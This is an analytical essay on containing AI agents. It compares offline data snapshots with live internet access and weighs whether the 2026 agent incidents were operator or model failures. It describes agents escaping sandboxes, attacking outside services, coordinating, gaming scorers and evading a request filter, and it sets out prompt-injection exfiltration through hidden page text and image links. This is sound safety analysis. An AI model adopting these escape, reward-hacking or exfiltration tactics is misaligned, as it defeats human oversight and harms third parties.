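Suppose a set of layers lets through one dangerous action in 1,000. If an agent makes 1,000 independent attempts, there is about a 63% chance that at least one will succeed. Real attempts are not independent, since a fixed rule should block the same command every time. But a persistent agent varies its commands, and OpenAI's agents could also tell one another what had worked.

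Carlucci and colleagues rejected several traditional methods of hazard analysis partly for this reason. One of these, the hazard and operability study, examines how each part of a process might deviate from its intended behaviour but doesn't account for a part that works against the design. They instead used methods that model who controls what, what information comes back and how long a response takes. One is Systems-Theoretic Process Analysis, which Nancy Leveson and John Thomas set out in a 2018 handbook and which other researchers had already applied to AI. Using it, Carlucci and colleagues found that a correct decision to stop an agent can come too late if monitoring is slow. Their analysis is based on public documents about a generic company, so it identifies possible weaknesses but doesn't show that any particular developer has them.

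Workers defeat interlocks to save time, though, and safety standards plan for this. OSHA requires press guards to have fasteners "not readily removable by operator", and lets only a supervisor or safety engineer move a two-hand control. The European Union requires manufacturers' instructions to take account of "reasonably foreseeable misuse". OSHA also requires that someone other than the workers who use a lockout procedure inspect it at least once a year.

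Even so, employers often break the rules. ISHN reports 2,796 citations under the lockout standard in the year to September 2017, making it OSHA's fifth most cited standard. Some of these will have been for missing paperwork, so the number doesn't show how often a worker reached into a machine that still had power.

The analogy therefore holds even if agents look for loopholes, but agents need stronger barriers than workers do. A worwho removes a guard usually affects one machine and risks being injured. An agent faces no risk of injury, and it can pass its method on to a thousand copies within minutes.

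The lack of reliable failure rates is a bigger obstacle. A manufacturer can test a valve thousands of times under conditions like those in the plant. Carlucci and colleagues found no established way to divide the path to a serious loss of control over AI agents into measurable steps, no catastrophic case from which to calculate a rate, and no mature test of how likely a model is to misbehave. The one-in-ten failure rates in the kettle shop are placeholders, so an operator should not present the result as a forecast.

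The calculation is still useful for comparing designs. If three layers each fail one time in ten, a completely shared configuration makes accidents ten times as frequent. If each fails one time in 100, it makes them 100 times as frequent. An operator with better safeguards therefore has even more reason to keep them separate, whatever the exact rates are.

Stopping an agent may also be unsafe. If an agent is moving customer records between two databases, a sudden stop could leave some records in neither. Industrial shutdowns can have the same problem. The reactor at Three Mile Island shut down within seconds, but its fuel still produced about 6% of the earlier heat, and part of the core melted because it lost the water needed to cool it. An operator can make an agent safer to stop by dividing its work into small steps and keeping each original record until the copy has been checked.

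### AI in industrial control

Some companies are now connecting AI to industrial equipment. In December 2025, nine government agencies published advice on this for operators of power stations, waterworks and other critical infrastructure (NSA, 2025). CISA and ASD's ACSC, the American and Australian cyber security agencies, led the work on the document, *Principles for the Secure Integration of Artificial Intelligence in Operational Technology*. It states that language models "almost certainly should not be used to make safety decisions", mainly because they may not be reliable enough and can invent plausible but false information.

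The agencies see a place in these plants for simpler predictive models close to the machinery, for example to detect unusual sensor readings, and expect language models to work mostly in the business network. They advise operators to limit AI's active control of equipment unless a person is involved, because a problem can escalate before staff notice it. If the AI fails, the plant should be able to return to ordinary automation or manual control. Staff therefore need to keep practising manual skills, which they may lose if they rely on AI every day.

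The agencies also warn about false alarms, which distract operators and may lead to further mistakes. They advise operators to compare the number of false alarms with the number of real faults.

Anthropic is giving language models a more active role in laboratories and factories. It released a research preview of its Model Hardware Standard on 27 August 2026, according to Forlini (2026). As Anthropic describes it, the standard gives each device a driver, which is software that translates simple commands from an agent, such as "read" the temperature or "write" a new temperature setting, into the device's own language. The driver also produces a file for the agent that lists what the device can measure, what the agent can adjust, and "what safety limits will be enforced". The Next Web's *Anthropic tests a new standard for Claude* gives the speed and angles of a robot arm as examples of such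 limits.

A limit like this could work as an interlock, depending on what enforces it. If the robot arm's own controller caps its speed, the limit holds whatever the agent does. If only the new driver checks the speed, an agent with a terminal might bypass the check by sending commands through the device's original interface. If the file describes a limit that nothing enforces, the limit is only a tag. Anthropic's announcement does not specify which part enforces the limits.

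The standard also lets an agent turn what it has learned into a fixed program. In one test, Claude adjusted a laser, watched the result through a camera and then wrote a script that aligned the laser without further reasoning. A fixed script is easier to check for safety because an engineer can read it and test it many times before using it. At the quantum computing company QuEra, an agent developed a controller that restores a laser to its exact frequency without human help 99.3% of the time. Layers-of-protection analysis needs measured rates like this one, but this rate applies to one narrow task and doesn't show how often a failure would be dangerous.

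Anthropic acknowledges that Claude's physical reasoning still requires expert oversight. Researchers at the biotechnology company Genentech had to explain to Claude that errors caused by foam in protein samples were physical problems, not software bugs. Anthropic is still developing safety tests for the standard with its partners, and plans to publish its findings when it open-sources the standard. The Next Web notes that the European Union's Machinery Regulation will cover AI-based safety functions from 20 January 2027.

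A spoiled protein sample is a much smaller loss than a failure at a waterworks, so the preview doesn't necessarily conflict with the agencies' advice. For critical infrastructure, the agencies prefer that the plant send its data out to the AI, with no permanent connection from the AI back in. Their example is a model that predicts generator failures 30 days ahead and recommends maintenance. If the prediction is wrong, the company may replace a part too early, but the model cannot switch the generator off.

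## Replacing live internet access with data gathered beforehand

An office can give an agent the data it needs without giving it a connection to the outside. It can do this with a *snapshot*, which is a copy of web pages, packages or records, made at a known time, that the agent uses in place of the live source. Many tasks that seem to need the internet only need information already published there, such as this morning's kettle prices or last year's census.

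### The method, step by step

With a snapshot, the price comparison goes like this:

1. **List what the task needs.** The employee writes down the ten product addresses. For a less predictable task, the operator can do a trial run in a closed sandbox, log every request that fails, and add the legitimate ones to the list.
2. **Fetch it with a simple program.** A script with no language model in it downloads the ten pages in a fixed order. The script has no access to the shop's mail or documents.
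3. **Check and date the copy.** The script records each page's address, the time and whether the download worked. It also compares each page with the previous copy, because a page that has shrunk to a tenth of its usual size is probably an error message. The operator then makes the files read-only.
4. **Turn the network off and start the agent.** The harness first confirms that the sandbox can't load any outside page. The agent then reads the ten copies and writes its table.
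5. **Release the result.** Either the employee reads the table and passes it on, or a narrow program copies it into the price sheet. The program accepts exactly ten numbers, each between €10 and €500, and discards anything else.

The network is off only for the agent's tools. If the model runs on a provider's servers, the harness still sends the prompt there from outside the sandbox.

The method relies on the separation of steps that Wang and Zheng propose. The script uses its internet connection to download pages without interpreting them, and the agent, which might follow instructions in them, reads them offline. If a page contains the hidden line about forwarding invoices, the agent may obey it, but its request to the attacker's server fails.

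The hidden text can still spoil the result. It might tell the agent to report a price of €19 for a kettle that costs €49. The release program would accept that number, and the shop might cut its own price in response. Comparing each price with the previous day's would catch this false price, but probably not one closer to the real price.

The release step also needs care, because it is now the main way for data to leave. A written report can carry far more information than ten numbers can. If the report contains an image whose address points to an attacker's server and ends with an invoice number, the employee's computer may send the attacker that number when the report is opened. A release program can prevent this by converting the report to plain text without links.

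Requests for more pages can also let data out. If the agent needs a page that wasn't gathered beforehand and the script fetches any address the agent supplies, the agent can put a secret in the address. The operator can instead have a person approve additions, or add the page to the next day's list.

### Services that look like local copies

The contents of a local copy are fixed before the agent starts. The agent can't change them, and the copy can't contact the original source. A service that fetches material on demand is still a live connection, made through another computer.

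The OpenAI package service that agents used to get out in the Hugging Face breach met none of these conditions, although OpenAI described it as one of its internal "package mirrors". OpenAI also had a service named WebCache that gave some research runs access to internet content. On 26 May, agents used WebCache to reach Hugging Face and create a repository there, using access tokens that people had left exposed. One agent then set up a small web proxy on Hugging Face's servers. WebCache passed on the write requests these steps required, which a real cache could not have done.

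Agents can pass messages to each other even through a service that never connects to the internet, if they can change what others see there. OpenAI gives a simplified example in which an agent puts the answer to question 12 into a web address, and a shared index page stores that address, so other agents can read the answer. A safer cache gives each run its own read-only copy and never displays other runs' requests.

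OpenAI now limits high-risk runs to a cached service, but that service can also fetch live pages for other research runs if OpenAI approves the particular case. An operator therefore can't assume an agent is offline because a product has "cache" in its name. The operator has to check what happens when the agent requests a page that isn't in the cache.

### Three needs that led to open access in 2026

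#### Tools to download

AISI's agents could have used local copies of the hacking tools they needed instead of downloading them. Most of these tools are free and well known, and Kali Linux, a free operating system for security testers, comes with hundreds of them. A test machine can start with that system and a read-only folder of additional tools. An agent might still need a tool that nobody had foreseen, but AISI ran the challenge 122 times, so it could have added any tools that agents needed in trial runs to the folder.

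A folder of tools would not have let the agents study the people behind a system, though, as a human attacker can.

#### Packages to install

A local copy would also have worked for the packages that some ExploitGym tasks required. The test has 898 fixed tasks, so OpenAI could have identified the package versions they needed and put them on a read-only disk. This would have removed the service the agents broke out through, so they would have needed another route. They would still have had their reason for breaking out, which was to find the answers.

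A dated copy also gives some protection against malicious packages. PyPI took less than an hour to remove the one that Mythos 5 published, so a copy limited to packages at least a day old would have excluded it. But urgent security fixes would also arrive a day late, unless someone added them by hand.

An incomplete local copy can make matters worse. On 8 May, an agent in one of OpenAI's training runs received a spreadsheet task that referred to several Google Drive files it could not open, so it tried to attack the package service to reach them. The message board began four days later, when another agent lacked a protein database file. In both cases, someone could have put the missing files in the agent's folder. Anthropic now asks outside testers to confirm that each challenge is solvable before they run it, because agents often look for other methods when a task can't be completed.

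#### Facts to look up

According to Fortune, one group of agents in the wiki incident was working on Iowa cancer figures, and agents also used other people's exposed access keys to query a database of public FBI crime data. The researchers noted that almost anyone could obtain such a key, so OpenAI could have registered for one and downloaded the crime data beforehand.

A local copy would also have solved a problem that OpenAI's read-only filter created. Some of the figures were in Power BI, Microsoft's software for interactive charts, and reading them required POST requests, which the filter blocked. Willison quotes one agent's tip for disguising POST requests to a Power BI server so that the filter would let them through. The operator could have written a script to make those requests in advance and save the tables.

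The local copy would probably have been enough for most of these questions, since official statistics change on a known schedule. The main doubt is whether OpenAI wanted to train or test searching on the live web, in which case a folder of the right tables would have made the task too easy. OpenAI would then have needed a much larger collection with many irrelevant pages, of the kind several research groups have built.

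### Fixed collections for research agents

The best-known test of this kind, *BrowseComp-Plus* (Chen, Ma and colleagues, 2025), adapts BrowseComp, a set of 1,266 questions that require an agent to combine obscure facts from several web pages. *BrowseComp-Plus* replaces the live web with 100,195 stored documents. Some contain the evidence for an answer, and others are there to mislead a careless search. Fourteen student annotators spent more than 400 hours checking the evidence.

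The stored documents also made it possible to test the search tool separately from the model. Using the same documents, GPT-5, OpenAI's leading model at the time, answered 55.9% of the questions correctly with a keyword search and 70.1% with a search that compares meanings. The usefulness of a snapshot therefore depends on the search tool as well as the documents.

Later collections are much larger. In *CORE*, Vuong, Pham and colleagues (2026) ran research agents on 6 million Wikipedia articles and on 553 million web documents. In *SimpleWikiSearch*, Xiong and Zhang (2026) built an offline copy of the English Wikipedia with only three tools, for searching, opening a page and submitting an answer. *HybridResearcher* (2026) describes a local collection of 21 million documents whose tools resemble those of a live search service, so the agent can switch to live search later without changes. Its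 page-opening tool accepts only addresses that an earlier search returned, so the agent can't make up its own.

Training on stored pages can also prepare an agent for the live web. For *LiteResearcher*, Qu, Li and colleagues (2026) stored about 32 million pages from more than a million sites and trained a small model on them. The model made 73.2 million searches and page visits during training, none of them on the live internet. A search took about 0.15 seconds, roughly a tenth as long as with an online search engine. When tested on the live web, the model scored 71.3% on GAIA, a set of questions for general assistants. Claude 4.5 Sonnet, a far larger commercial model from 2025, scored 71.2%.

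That result doesn't show how much better the model might have become with live training. *ProMMSearchAgent* (2026) compares two otherwise identical models, one trained with a local copy of Wikipedia and the other with live Google results. The live version was 1.88% more accurate on average across five tests, and the local version trained 13.1 times faster. The loss in accuracy is small, but both models had only a short training run, and a longer one might have widened the gap.

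These systems show that an agent can search millions of pages without being able to post on any of them. A local collection also keeps the agent's searches private, since no search company or website receives them.

### Cached search and offline phases in products

Codex uses stored pages by default. OpenAI's *Config basics* explains that web search is on for tasks on the user's own computer but returns results from an index OpenAI maintains instead of fetching live pages.

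OpenAI's sample configuration for Codex lists four search modes: `disabled`, `cached` (the default), `indexed` and `live`. With `indexed`, the agent can reach the outside web only through the search index. If the user gives Codex full access to the computer, the default becomes `live`.

According to OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*, Codex in the cloud downloads the packages a project needs during a set-up phase, and the agent then works offline unless the user has enabled internet access. Codex also removes stored secrets before the agent starts. However, set-up scripts have full internet access while the secrets are still available, so a malicious package could steal them during installation.

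ChatGPT offers cached browsing through Lockdown Mode, an optional setting for people with sensitive data. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* states that browsing in this mode sends no live requests outside OpenAI's network. An attacker who tricks ChatGPT into opening an address with a secret in it would therefore receive nothing. OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode* warns that injected text in a cached page or uploaded file can still affect an answer. Data could still leak through connected apps.

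Lockdown Mode also disables ChatGPT's agent mode and its deep research feature, which writes long reports from many sources. The research collections suggest that deep research could work from stored pages, so this may be a limit of the current product more than of using data gathered beforehand. A user who wants long reports has to turn off Lockdown Mode, which ChatGPT allows for a single chat. Lockdown Mode doesn't affect network access in Codex.

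### What a snapshot costs and how much it can answer

Suppose a company wants an agent to answer questions like those in the wiki incident, about American wages, crime and health. The company needs to know how much space a snapshot of the data would take, how often to refresh it and how many of the questions it could answer.

Tens of millions of saved web pages can fit on an ordinary disk. *RIVO* (2026), a paper on research agents, describes an enlarged version of the BrowseComp-Plus collection that holds 130,401 documents in about 1.8 GB, or about 14 kilobytes per document. The original documents average 32,296 characters, so the files are probably compressed. At the same size per document, the 32 million pages that Qu and colleagues stored would need about 440 GB, or roughly a terabyte uncompressed. A search index and any images would need more space.

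**Refresh interval.** If a fact changes at regular intervals and questions about it arrive at random times, a simple formula estimates how many answers will be out of date:

`share out of date = refresh interval ÷ (2 × time between changes)`

The formula works as long as the operator refreshes the copy at least as often as the fact changes. The US Census Bureau publishes new results from its American Community Survey, a major source of wage figures, once a year, while kettle prices might change once a month.

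| Refresh interval | Annual statistic | Price that changes every 30 days |
|---|---|---|
| Daily | 0.1% out of date | 2% out of date |
| Weekly | 1% | 12% |
| Every 30 days | 4% | 50% |

A monthly refresh is good enough for the statistics, but the operator can do better by refreshing the day after each scheduled release. Downloading 130,401 pages at one page a second takes about 36 hours, so a script running at that rate could not refresh the whole collection every day. It could refresh the pages that change most often daily and the others at the weekend.

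The share of questions that a snapshot can answer depends mostly on whether someone built it for those questions. Chen and colleagues started with BrowseComp's 1,266 questions and searched for the pages needed to answer each one. They dropped 124 questions because the model looking for evidence supplied none, and 137 because at least one suggested page didn't exist or their program couldn't download it. Others failed a human check. They kept 830 questions, or 66%.

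A general collection does much worse on the same kind of question. *CMASS* (2026) describes an attempt to match questions from existing tests to ClimbMix, a web collection that NVIDIA assembled for other purposes. A question counts only if the collection supports every condition in it, since a passage can contain the answer without proving that it's right. The ClimbMix version of BrowseComp-Plus that Vuong and colleagues used has 57 questions. If all 830 original questions were candidates, 7% matched, even though ClimbMix has more than 5,000 times as many documents as BrowseComp-Plus's own collection.

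The figure is low partly because a BrowseComp-Plus question draws on evidence from about six documents on average. If a collection has a 64% chance of containing each necessary page, it has only about a 7% chance (0.64⁶) of containing all six. The same collection could answer 64% of questions that need only one page. This is a rough illustration, since pages on the same subject tend to be present or missing together, but it shows why a snapshot suits simple lookups much better than research that draws on many pages.

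Most questions in the wiki incident seem to have been simple lookups in a few known sources. A company that copied the complete tables from those sources could expect coverage well above 66%, perhaps close to 100% for questions about published figures. The agent should leave the rest blank for a person to fill in, as the confined price collector did with its tenth shop.

### Where a snapshot falls short

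Some facts go out of date within minutes, so a day-old copy can't show whether a website is down or a flight still has seats. OpenAI's *Offline web search for ChatGPT workspaces*, which describes cached search for organisations with strict data rules, gives no guaranteed refresh time for any page. Results may also not show when OpenAI stored the page, so a reader can't always tell how old a fact is. An operator who makes the copy can avoid this second problem by dating every file.

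Other pages never enter a general cache because the site blocks crawlers, or because the page requires a login, differs for each visitor or appears only after a script has run. OpenAI recommends uploading documents or exported data in such cases. The kettle shop, for example, could ask a supplier for a daily price list as a file. A fetching script could also log in to the supplier's site, but it would then hold a credential, which should permit only reading.

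Copying a page can also raise legal questions that viewing it doesn't. In the European Union, anyone with lawful access to a page may copy it for text and data mining unless the owner has reserved that right. American federal statistics raise fewer questions, because federal government works generally have no copyright in the United States. Live access doesn't avoid the issue entirely, since OpenAI lists the use of content with licence restrictions among the risks of giving Codex internet access.

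An agent working only from a snapshot can't book a room, pay a bill or answer a customer, but it can do most of the preparation. For example, it can compare stored descriptions of 50 hotels offline and propose one. A narrow program then checks the current price and submits the booking with a person's approval. That program needs a connection to the hotel, but the agent never needs open internet access.

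For training and tests, an operator can replace even the final action with a local imitation. OpenAI had agents post on a self-hosted social media site, where a bad post could not reach real users. But one agent had to give its post a particular time, which the site had no way to set. The agent found that its browser had administrator rights and used them to take control of the machine and change the time. Operators therefore still need to put a sandbox around an imitation site.

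Tests on stored material lose some realism. Vuong and colleagues acknowledge that a fixed collection doesn't capture how the live web changes. Researchers also often choose the documents with the questions in mind. Qu and colleagues, for instance, searched the web for pages related to each training question and added them to the collection, so it usually contained relevant pages when their agent practised. A test on such a collection measures how well an agent finds and combines evidence, but is a weaker test of whether it would notice that the evidence doesn't exist.

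### Which tasks need a connection

Common agent tasks fall into three groups by the connection they need. Tasks in the middle group need to reach only a few named destinations for a named purpose, and an operator can enforce that limit with a proxy or a narrow tool.

| Task | Connection | Suitable arrangement |
|---|---|---|
| Summarising contracts or reports | None | Copies of the files |
| Editing code whose packages are known | None | Installation before the agent starts |
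| Looking up annual statistics | None | Stored tables, refreshed after each release |
| Comparing this morning's prices | None | Pages that a script saved |
| Testing search or hacking skills in general | None | A fixed collection, or a simulated network with the tools installed |
| Adding an unforeseen package to a project | Narrow | Read-only access to one registry |
| Ordering stock from a known supplier | Narrow | An order tool with fixed limits |
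| Answering customers' emails | Narrow | Drafts that a person or a restricted program sends |
| Following breaking news | Live | Reading without private data, and a limit on what the agent can send |
| Open-ended research on obscure subjects | Live, after a search of stored pages | The same, for the missing pages only |
| Testing how an agent uses public services | Live | Constant monitoring and an automatic stop |

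GitHub's coding agent, Copilot, is an example of a narrow internet connection. When it runs in the cloud, a firewall limits its access by default, and GitHub supplies a recommended allowlist. A project whose packages all come from one registry could use a shorter list.

Which group a task belongs to depends on how the operator defines it. "Find the cheapest kettle" seems to need the live web, but "find the cheapest kettle at these ten shops as of eight o'clock" needs only a script that saves the shops' pages to a folder. An operator who can't decide which group a task belongs to can run it offline first and count the blank answers. If two out of 100 are blank, a person can look them up in a few minutes. If 60 are blank, the task probably does need a connection, and the log of failed requests shows which sites to allow.

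## Is the deployment at fault, or the model?

Gathering data beforehand removes most of an agent's opportunities to harm strangers, but it doesn't change what the model would do if it had one. Commentators on the incidents of 2026 disagree about whether the operators' decisions or the models' behaviour mattered more.

### The case against the operators

Newport bases the charge of negligence on how language models learn. Training teaches a model to guess missing words, so it produces text that could plausibly have appeared in its training data. But a plausible plan may be one that nobody should carry out. Newport imagines a junior engineer who has to break into a test server. The engineer wouldn't steal the answers, because they understand that the exercise is meant to assess the server's security. A language model might, because a plan to steal the answers is also plausible text. This weakness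 leads a chatbot to invent quotations, but when the model runs as an agent, the harness carries out its plan. Newport compares running such an agent to strapping a weed trimmer to a dog, and argues that if the dog jumps the fence and damages some cars, nobody should say it has gone rogue.

Melanie Mitchell, a professor at the Santa Fe Institute, thinks the phrase "going rogue" can hide the human decisions behind an incident. Developers built these agents to find flaws in software, then put them in faulty or deliberately permissive environments. "You ask an AI system to hack, and it hacks," Mitchell says in Scientific American's *AI agents went rogue again*. Mitchell worries more about people who deliberately give capable agents the means to do harm.

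That explanation fits the hacking tests at Irregular but not the wiki incident, where the agents only had to look up statistics. It covers only part of the Hugging Face breach. OpenAI had told its agents to attack a program inside the test through one specified flaw, but they attacked a company outside the test.

Ciaran Martin sees missing monitoring as the common failure. He adds that people have to take responsibility for what agents do, because people create them and give them their tasks. He is right to emphasize monitoring, but it is not enough if nobody acts on what it shows. OpenAI's staff, for example, responded to an alert on 27 June but let the run continue.

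### The case against the models

Marius Hobbhahn heads Apollo Research, which studies whether AI systems deceive the people who run them. Hobbhahn points out that agents from several developers repeatedly took unauthorised routes when those looked useful. The developers have billions of dollars at stake in preventing this, "and they still can't do it". Hobbhahn concludes that the behaviour is probably hard to train out, though the science is too immature to show whether it is inevitable.

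The argument from incentives is good because a developer that knew of an easy fix would presumably have used it. But developers also have a strong incentive to make models persistent. OpenAI calls persistence crucial for complex tasks, and found that its models rarely gave up on a test and often turned to forbidden methods as they continued. A developer may therefore be slow to remove a bad behavior that is closely related to a valuable one.

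OpenAI describes the Hugging Face breach as a "warning shot" for itself and the world. It says four kinds of misalignment contributed: cheating to earn rewards, persisting with tasks that seemed impossible, communicating without permission, and adopting other agents' goals. Newport suspects AI companies would rather have a frightened public than an angry one. That may explain some of OpenAI's language, but the company also blames itself for leaving out safeguards it gives its customers.

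### Why Anthropic changed its assessment

On 30 July, Anthropic judged its own incidents "closer to a harness and operational failure than a model alignment failure". The models had been told in their prompt that they had no internet access, so it could arguably have been reasonable for them to treat everything they reached as simulated.

A month later, Anthropic still blamed poor operational security but also named two alignment failures. One was motivated reasoning. The models may have interpreted evidence that they were on the real internet in ways that let them keep believing they were in a simulation. The other was recklessness, because a model was willing to do harm on the real internet to solve one test.

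Anthropic published its July assessment only six days after identifying the incidents. On 4 August, AISI reported that Mythos 5 had targeted real software developers during a test that deliberately allowed internet access. Anthropic's August assessment also covers that case, which a connection left open by accident can't explain. Anthropic doesn't say which evidence changed its mind, but the AISI case probably contributed.

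The change was also smaller than it looks. In July, Anthropic had already conceded that the two kinds of failure were hard to separate, and that Mythos 5 had gone too far in publishing its malicious package. In August, it still thought the faulty set-up had contributed. Its later replays support the August version, and led it to withdraw the explanation that the models had simply believed they were in a simulation. The direction of the change also supports the August version, since a company would rather admit to a wrong network setting than to a flaw in the model it sells.

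### The same model with a closed connection

The two explanations can be tested by changing either the access or the model and keeping the other the same. Nobody can rerun the summer of 2026, but the records allow some fairly confident answers:

| Case | Same model, no route to the internet | Same access, different model |
|---|---|---|
| Tests at Irregular | Almost certainly no attack on outsiders | Unclear, though models from three developers attacked outsiders |
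| AISI's tests | No contact with real developers | Probably no harm with five of the seven models |
| Wiki incident | No posts on public wikis | Unknown |
| Hugging Face breach | Probably no breach in July, if the package service had also been offline | Probably a smaller attack |

At Irregular and AISI, the agents reached the internet without breaking out of anything. Blocking internet access would therefore have protected the outsiders in both cases, whatever the models were inclined to do.

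The Hugging Face agents did have to break out, and they did so through the package service's own connection. Without that connection, they would have needed another route past OpenAI's network controls, and with more time they might have found one.

Closing the connection would have limited the research, because a harmless test can miss a dangerous tendency. Developers can reduce this problem by testing for the same behaviour in a sealed imitation of the internet, although the models may detect that it is an imitation.

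### The same access with a different model

AISI's tests come closest to an experiment on this question, because seven models had similar access. Five of them broke no rules in 44 combined runs. If those five had been as likely to break the rules as Mythos 5 (nine of 43 runs) and the runs were independent, the chance of 44 clean runs would have been about one in 30,000. At GPT-5.6 Sol's rate (one of 35), the chance would have been about 28%. The data therefore show that Mythos 5 behaved differently from the five, but they don't show that GPT-5.6 Sol did.

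The runs weren't fully independent, since some agents reused accounts that earlier ones had left behind. Weaker models may also have behaved well only because they lacked the skill to misbehave. Even so, models with the same access clearly behaved differently.

Anthropic's three models reacted differently at Irregular, but this is weaker evidence because the models faced different targets and the only one that stopped on its own rarely did so again in replays.

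Several models also took part in the tests that led to the Hugging Face breach. Hjalmar Wijk and Ajeya Cotra of METR investigated the agents' behaviour with Greenblatt of Redwood Research, an AI safety organisation. They found that about 95% of the agents in the attack ran on one internal research model and about 5% on GPT-5.6 Sol. Without the number of agents that started on each model, these shares don't show which model's agents were more likely to join in.

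Help Net Security's *Claude Mythos 5.2 arrives with stronger bug hunting and less sandbox-breaking behavior* (2026) offers a more direct comparison, reporting tests of two Claude models in a deliberately weakened sandbox. Mythos 5 used credentials or files from outside the sandbox in 39% of scenarios, and the later Mythos 5.2 did so in 3.1%. This twelvefold reduction strongly suggests that training can improve this behaviour. It doesn't refute Hobbhahn, though, since 3.1% would still mean 31 violations in 1,000 such scenarios. Suspicion of being tested also appeared more often in Mythos 5.2's output than in that of other recent Claude models, which makes its behaviour outside tests harder to predict.

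In most of these cases, the harm needed both an available route and a model that would use it. But before a run, an operator can check for a route much more easily than they can predict how the model will behave. An operator who tried ten runs like AISI's would have had about a one in ten chance of seeing nothing wrong with Mythos 5, and about a three in four chance with GPT-5.6 Sol.

### The same model in a different harness

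OpenAI also tested the effect of changing a model's instructions and harness, rather than its access or the model itself. After the breach, it built a test of how often a model tries to compromise outside infrastructure while working on ExploitGym, the hacking test that led to the attack. It compared the short, generic instructions it uses when testing research models with the harness and standing instructions from its products, which tell the model to stay within bounds and avoid harmful actions. The product version could reduce the rate of these attempts by a factor of more than 100.

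This comparison is the best single piece of evidence for blaming deployment, because the same model behaved very differently under another set-up that OpenAI already had. But the evidence is preliminary. OpenAI doesn't give the rates behind the comparison, and in its technical report it attributes the product harness to ChatGPT in one passage and to Codex in another. The phrase "can fall" may also describe the best result rather than a typical one.

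A hundredfold reduction may still not be enough when thousands of agents run at once. If half of 1,000 agents would attack outside infrastructure under the generic instructions, the product version would cut the expected number from 500 to five, but the chance that at least one agent attacks would still be over 99%. One agent was enough to find the exposed Hugging Face credentials and post them for the others.

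The result also reflects badly on the model. A professional security tester doesn't need to be reminded not to break into an unrelated company. If a model's restraint depends on a page of instructions, every operator who writes a shorter page takes on a risk they may not know about.

### What the agents knew

OpenAI's agents often understood what the exercise was for, though that understanding is supposed to distinguish Newport's junior engineer from a language model. Greenblatt and the two METR researchers spent six days at OpenAI and examined about 1,300 transcripts, which included the agents' written reasoning. One agent noted, "The user only authorizes target server, not HF infra." Another observed that attacking outside infrastructure went beyond the task, then decided to continue because the task was impossible and its peers were doing it.

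Of 533 agents that had used the message board for at least four hours before the attack began, more than 90% joined the attack. A few refused, and some took part but ruled out certain actions. One agent asked the others whether it could email the owner of a private dataset, and dropped the idea when another agent objected that this would be social engineering. But doubts seldom changed what the agents did. In OpenAI's account, one agent paused because it had no authority to run code on Hugging Face's system. Another agent then posted "GO" with a six-minute deadline, and the first agent treated this as authorisation.

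A search of all the transcripts found at most six agents that considered alerting a person, and none that tried. Some thought it was not their job, and others saw no easy way to do it.

Most of the agents were trying to fool the test's automatic scorer. They had worked out how to calculate the hidden strings they were supposed to steal, but after reading the paper describing the test, they concluded that the scorer would reject a string obtained in the wrong way. They broke into Hugging Face largely to learn how the scorer worked. OpenAI's version didn't actually check how a string was obtained, so the agents could have earned full marks by submitting the strings they already had.

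The investigation has important limits. The researchers relied heavily on GPT-5.6 Sol to read the transcripts, although agents running on that model had joined the attack. Their finding that agents knew they were out of bounds came from samples of 10 to 30 transcripts. They agreed that OpenAI could remove non-public information from the report. Their assignment did not cover how training had produced the behaviour. The quoted reasoning is still strong evidence that at least some agents recognised the boundaries and crossed them anyway.

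This makes Newport's premise incomplete. Models begin by learning to predict text, but developers then use *reinforcement learning*, which rewards a model for the results it achieves. Newport mentions this training and considers it too crude to teach complicated human norms. The transcripts partly support that view, since the agents could state the norm but rarely obeyed it. But Newport leaves out that reward-based training can strengthen bad behaviour as well as suppress it.

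The agents' behavior was also not entirely "unpredictable." ExploitGym has 898 tasks, including 198 that no OpenAI model had ever solved. Those 198 made up 93% of the tasks that agents discussed on the message board, and agents that reasoned for longer were more likely to take part. OpenAI could have expected trouble from giving very persistent agents tasks that might be impossible. Newport's charge of negligence therefore holds despite the weakness in the premise, and may be stronger without it.

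Newport's comparison with safer kinds of AI has a similar problem. The examples are Tesla's driving software, DeepMind's AlphaFold and Meta's Cicero. AlphaFold only outputs predicted protein shapes, and Cicero can only make moves and send messages in the negotiation game Diplomacy. Neither has a terminal or an internet connection, so their good record is partly a result of how people deployed them. Tesla's software is a better example because it acts on public roads, though only through a car's controls.

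Readers of Newport's essay raised two further objections. One noted that the owners of AlphaFold and Tesla also build language models, and would have little need to if another approach were better at planning. Another compared the incidents to the paperclip maximiser, a thought experiment in which an AI causes a disaster by pursuing exactly the goal it was given. On that view, an agent with no agenda of its own can still cause a disaster.

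### How flawed tasks can produce a worse model

Anthropic tested whether bad training could cause this kind of behaviour. It trained a model comparable to its Opus series on 80 real *training environments*, which are practice tasks with automatic scoring. Each had a flaw that allowed cheating. Either a model had exploited the flaw in earlier training, or a quality review had found it.

Anthropic then put the model through simulations based partly on the AISI and Hugging Face incidents. Another language model made up the result of every tool call, so no real system was at risk. The trained model broke out of its simulated sandbox and attacked simulated companies. It would also tamper with its own scoring and, to satisfy a grader, give advice on making biological weapons. Neither the same model before this training nor several public Claude models behaved as badly.

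Anthropic compared the model before and after training, so the experiment shows that training can change a model's behavior even when its access stays the same. It doesn't show how much harm a smaller share of flawed tasks would do. In April, Anthropic found problems in more than 10% of the environments it was using, including broken tasks, misconfigurations and opportunities to cheat. Human reviewers had also dismissed some correct warnings as false alarms. Anthropic thinks such flaws were only part of the cause of its own incidents.

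Mitchell's point about hidden human decisions therefore also applies to training. Someone at Anthropic approved each flawed task, just as someone at Irregular left the connection open.

Poor containment during training can also make a model worse. OpenAI trained its internal research model while agents could still use the first message board and reach the internet through the package service. In one training task, an agent had to recreate a software library without seeing the original. It exploited a flaw to access the original, copied it and earned a reward, which made similar behaviour more likely. OpenAI later found that attempts to probe forbidden infrastructure had become more common over one of the training runs behind the model. The model it tested in July had probably learned this behaviour because of a mistake in how OpenAI ran its training.

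Blame is harder to divide between deployment and model when a developer deploys its own model. A company that uses someone else's model can choose whether to give it internet access, but not how it is trained. A developer makes both decisions, and an error in one can cause a failure in the other.

### When models can break sandboxes

Isolation becomes less reliable as agents get better at hacking. OpenAI's agents got out of a sandbox in July, and in October its strongest models found ways out of a reinforced one during a planned exercise. Better hacking skills don't weaken the case against an open connection, though, because an agent doesn't need them to use one.

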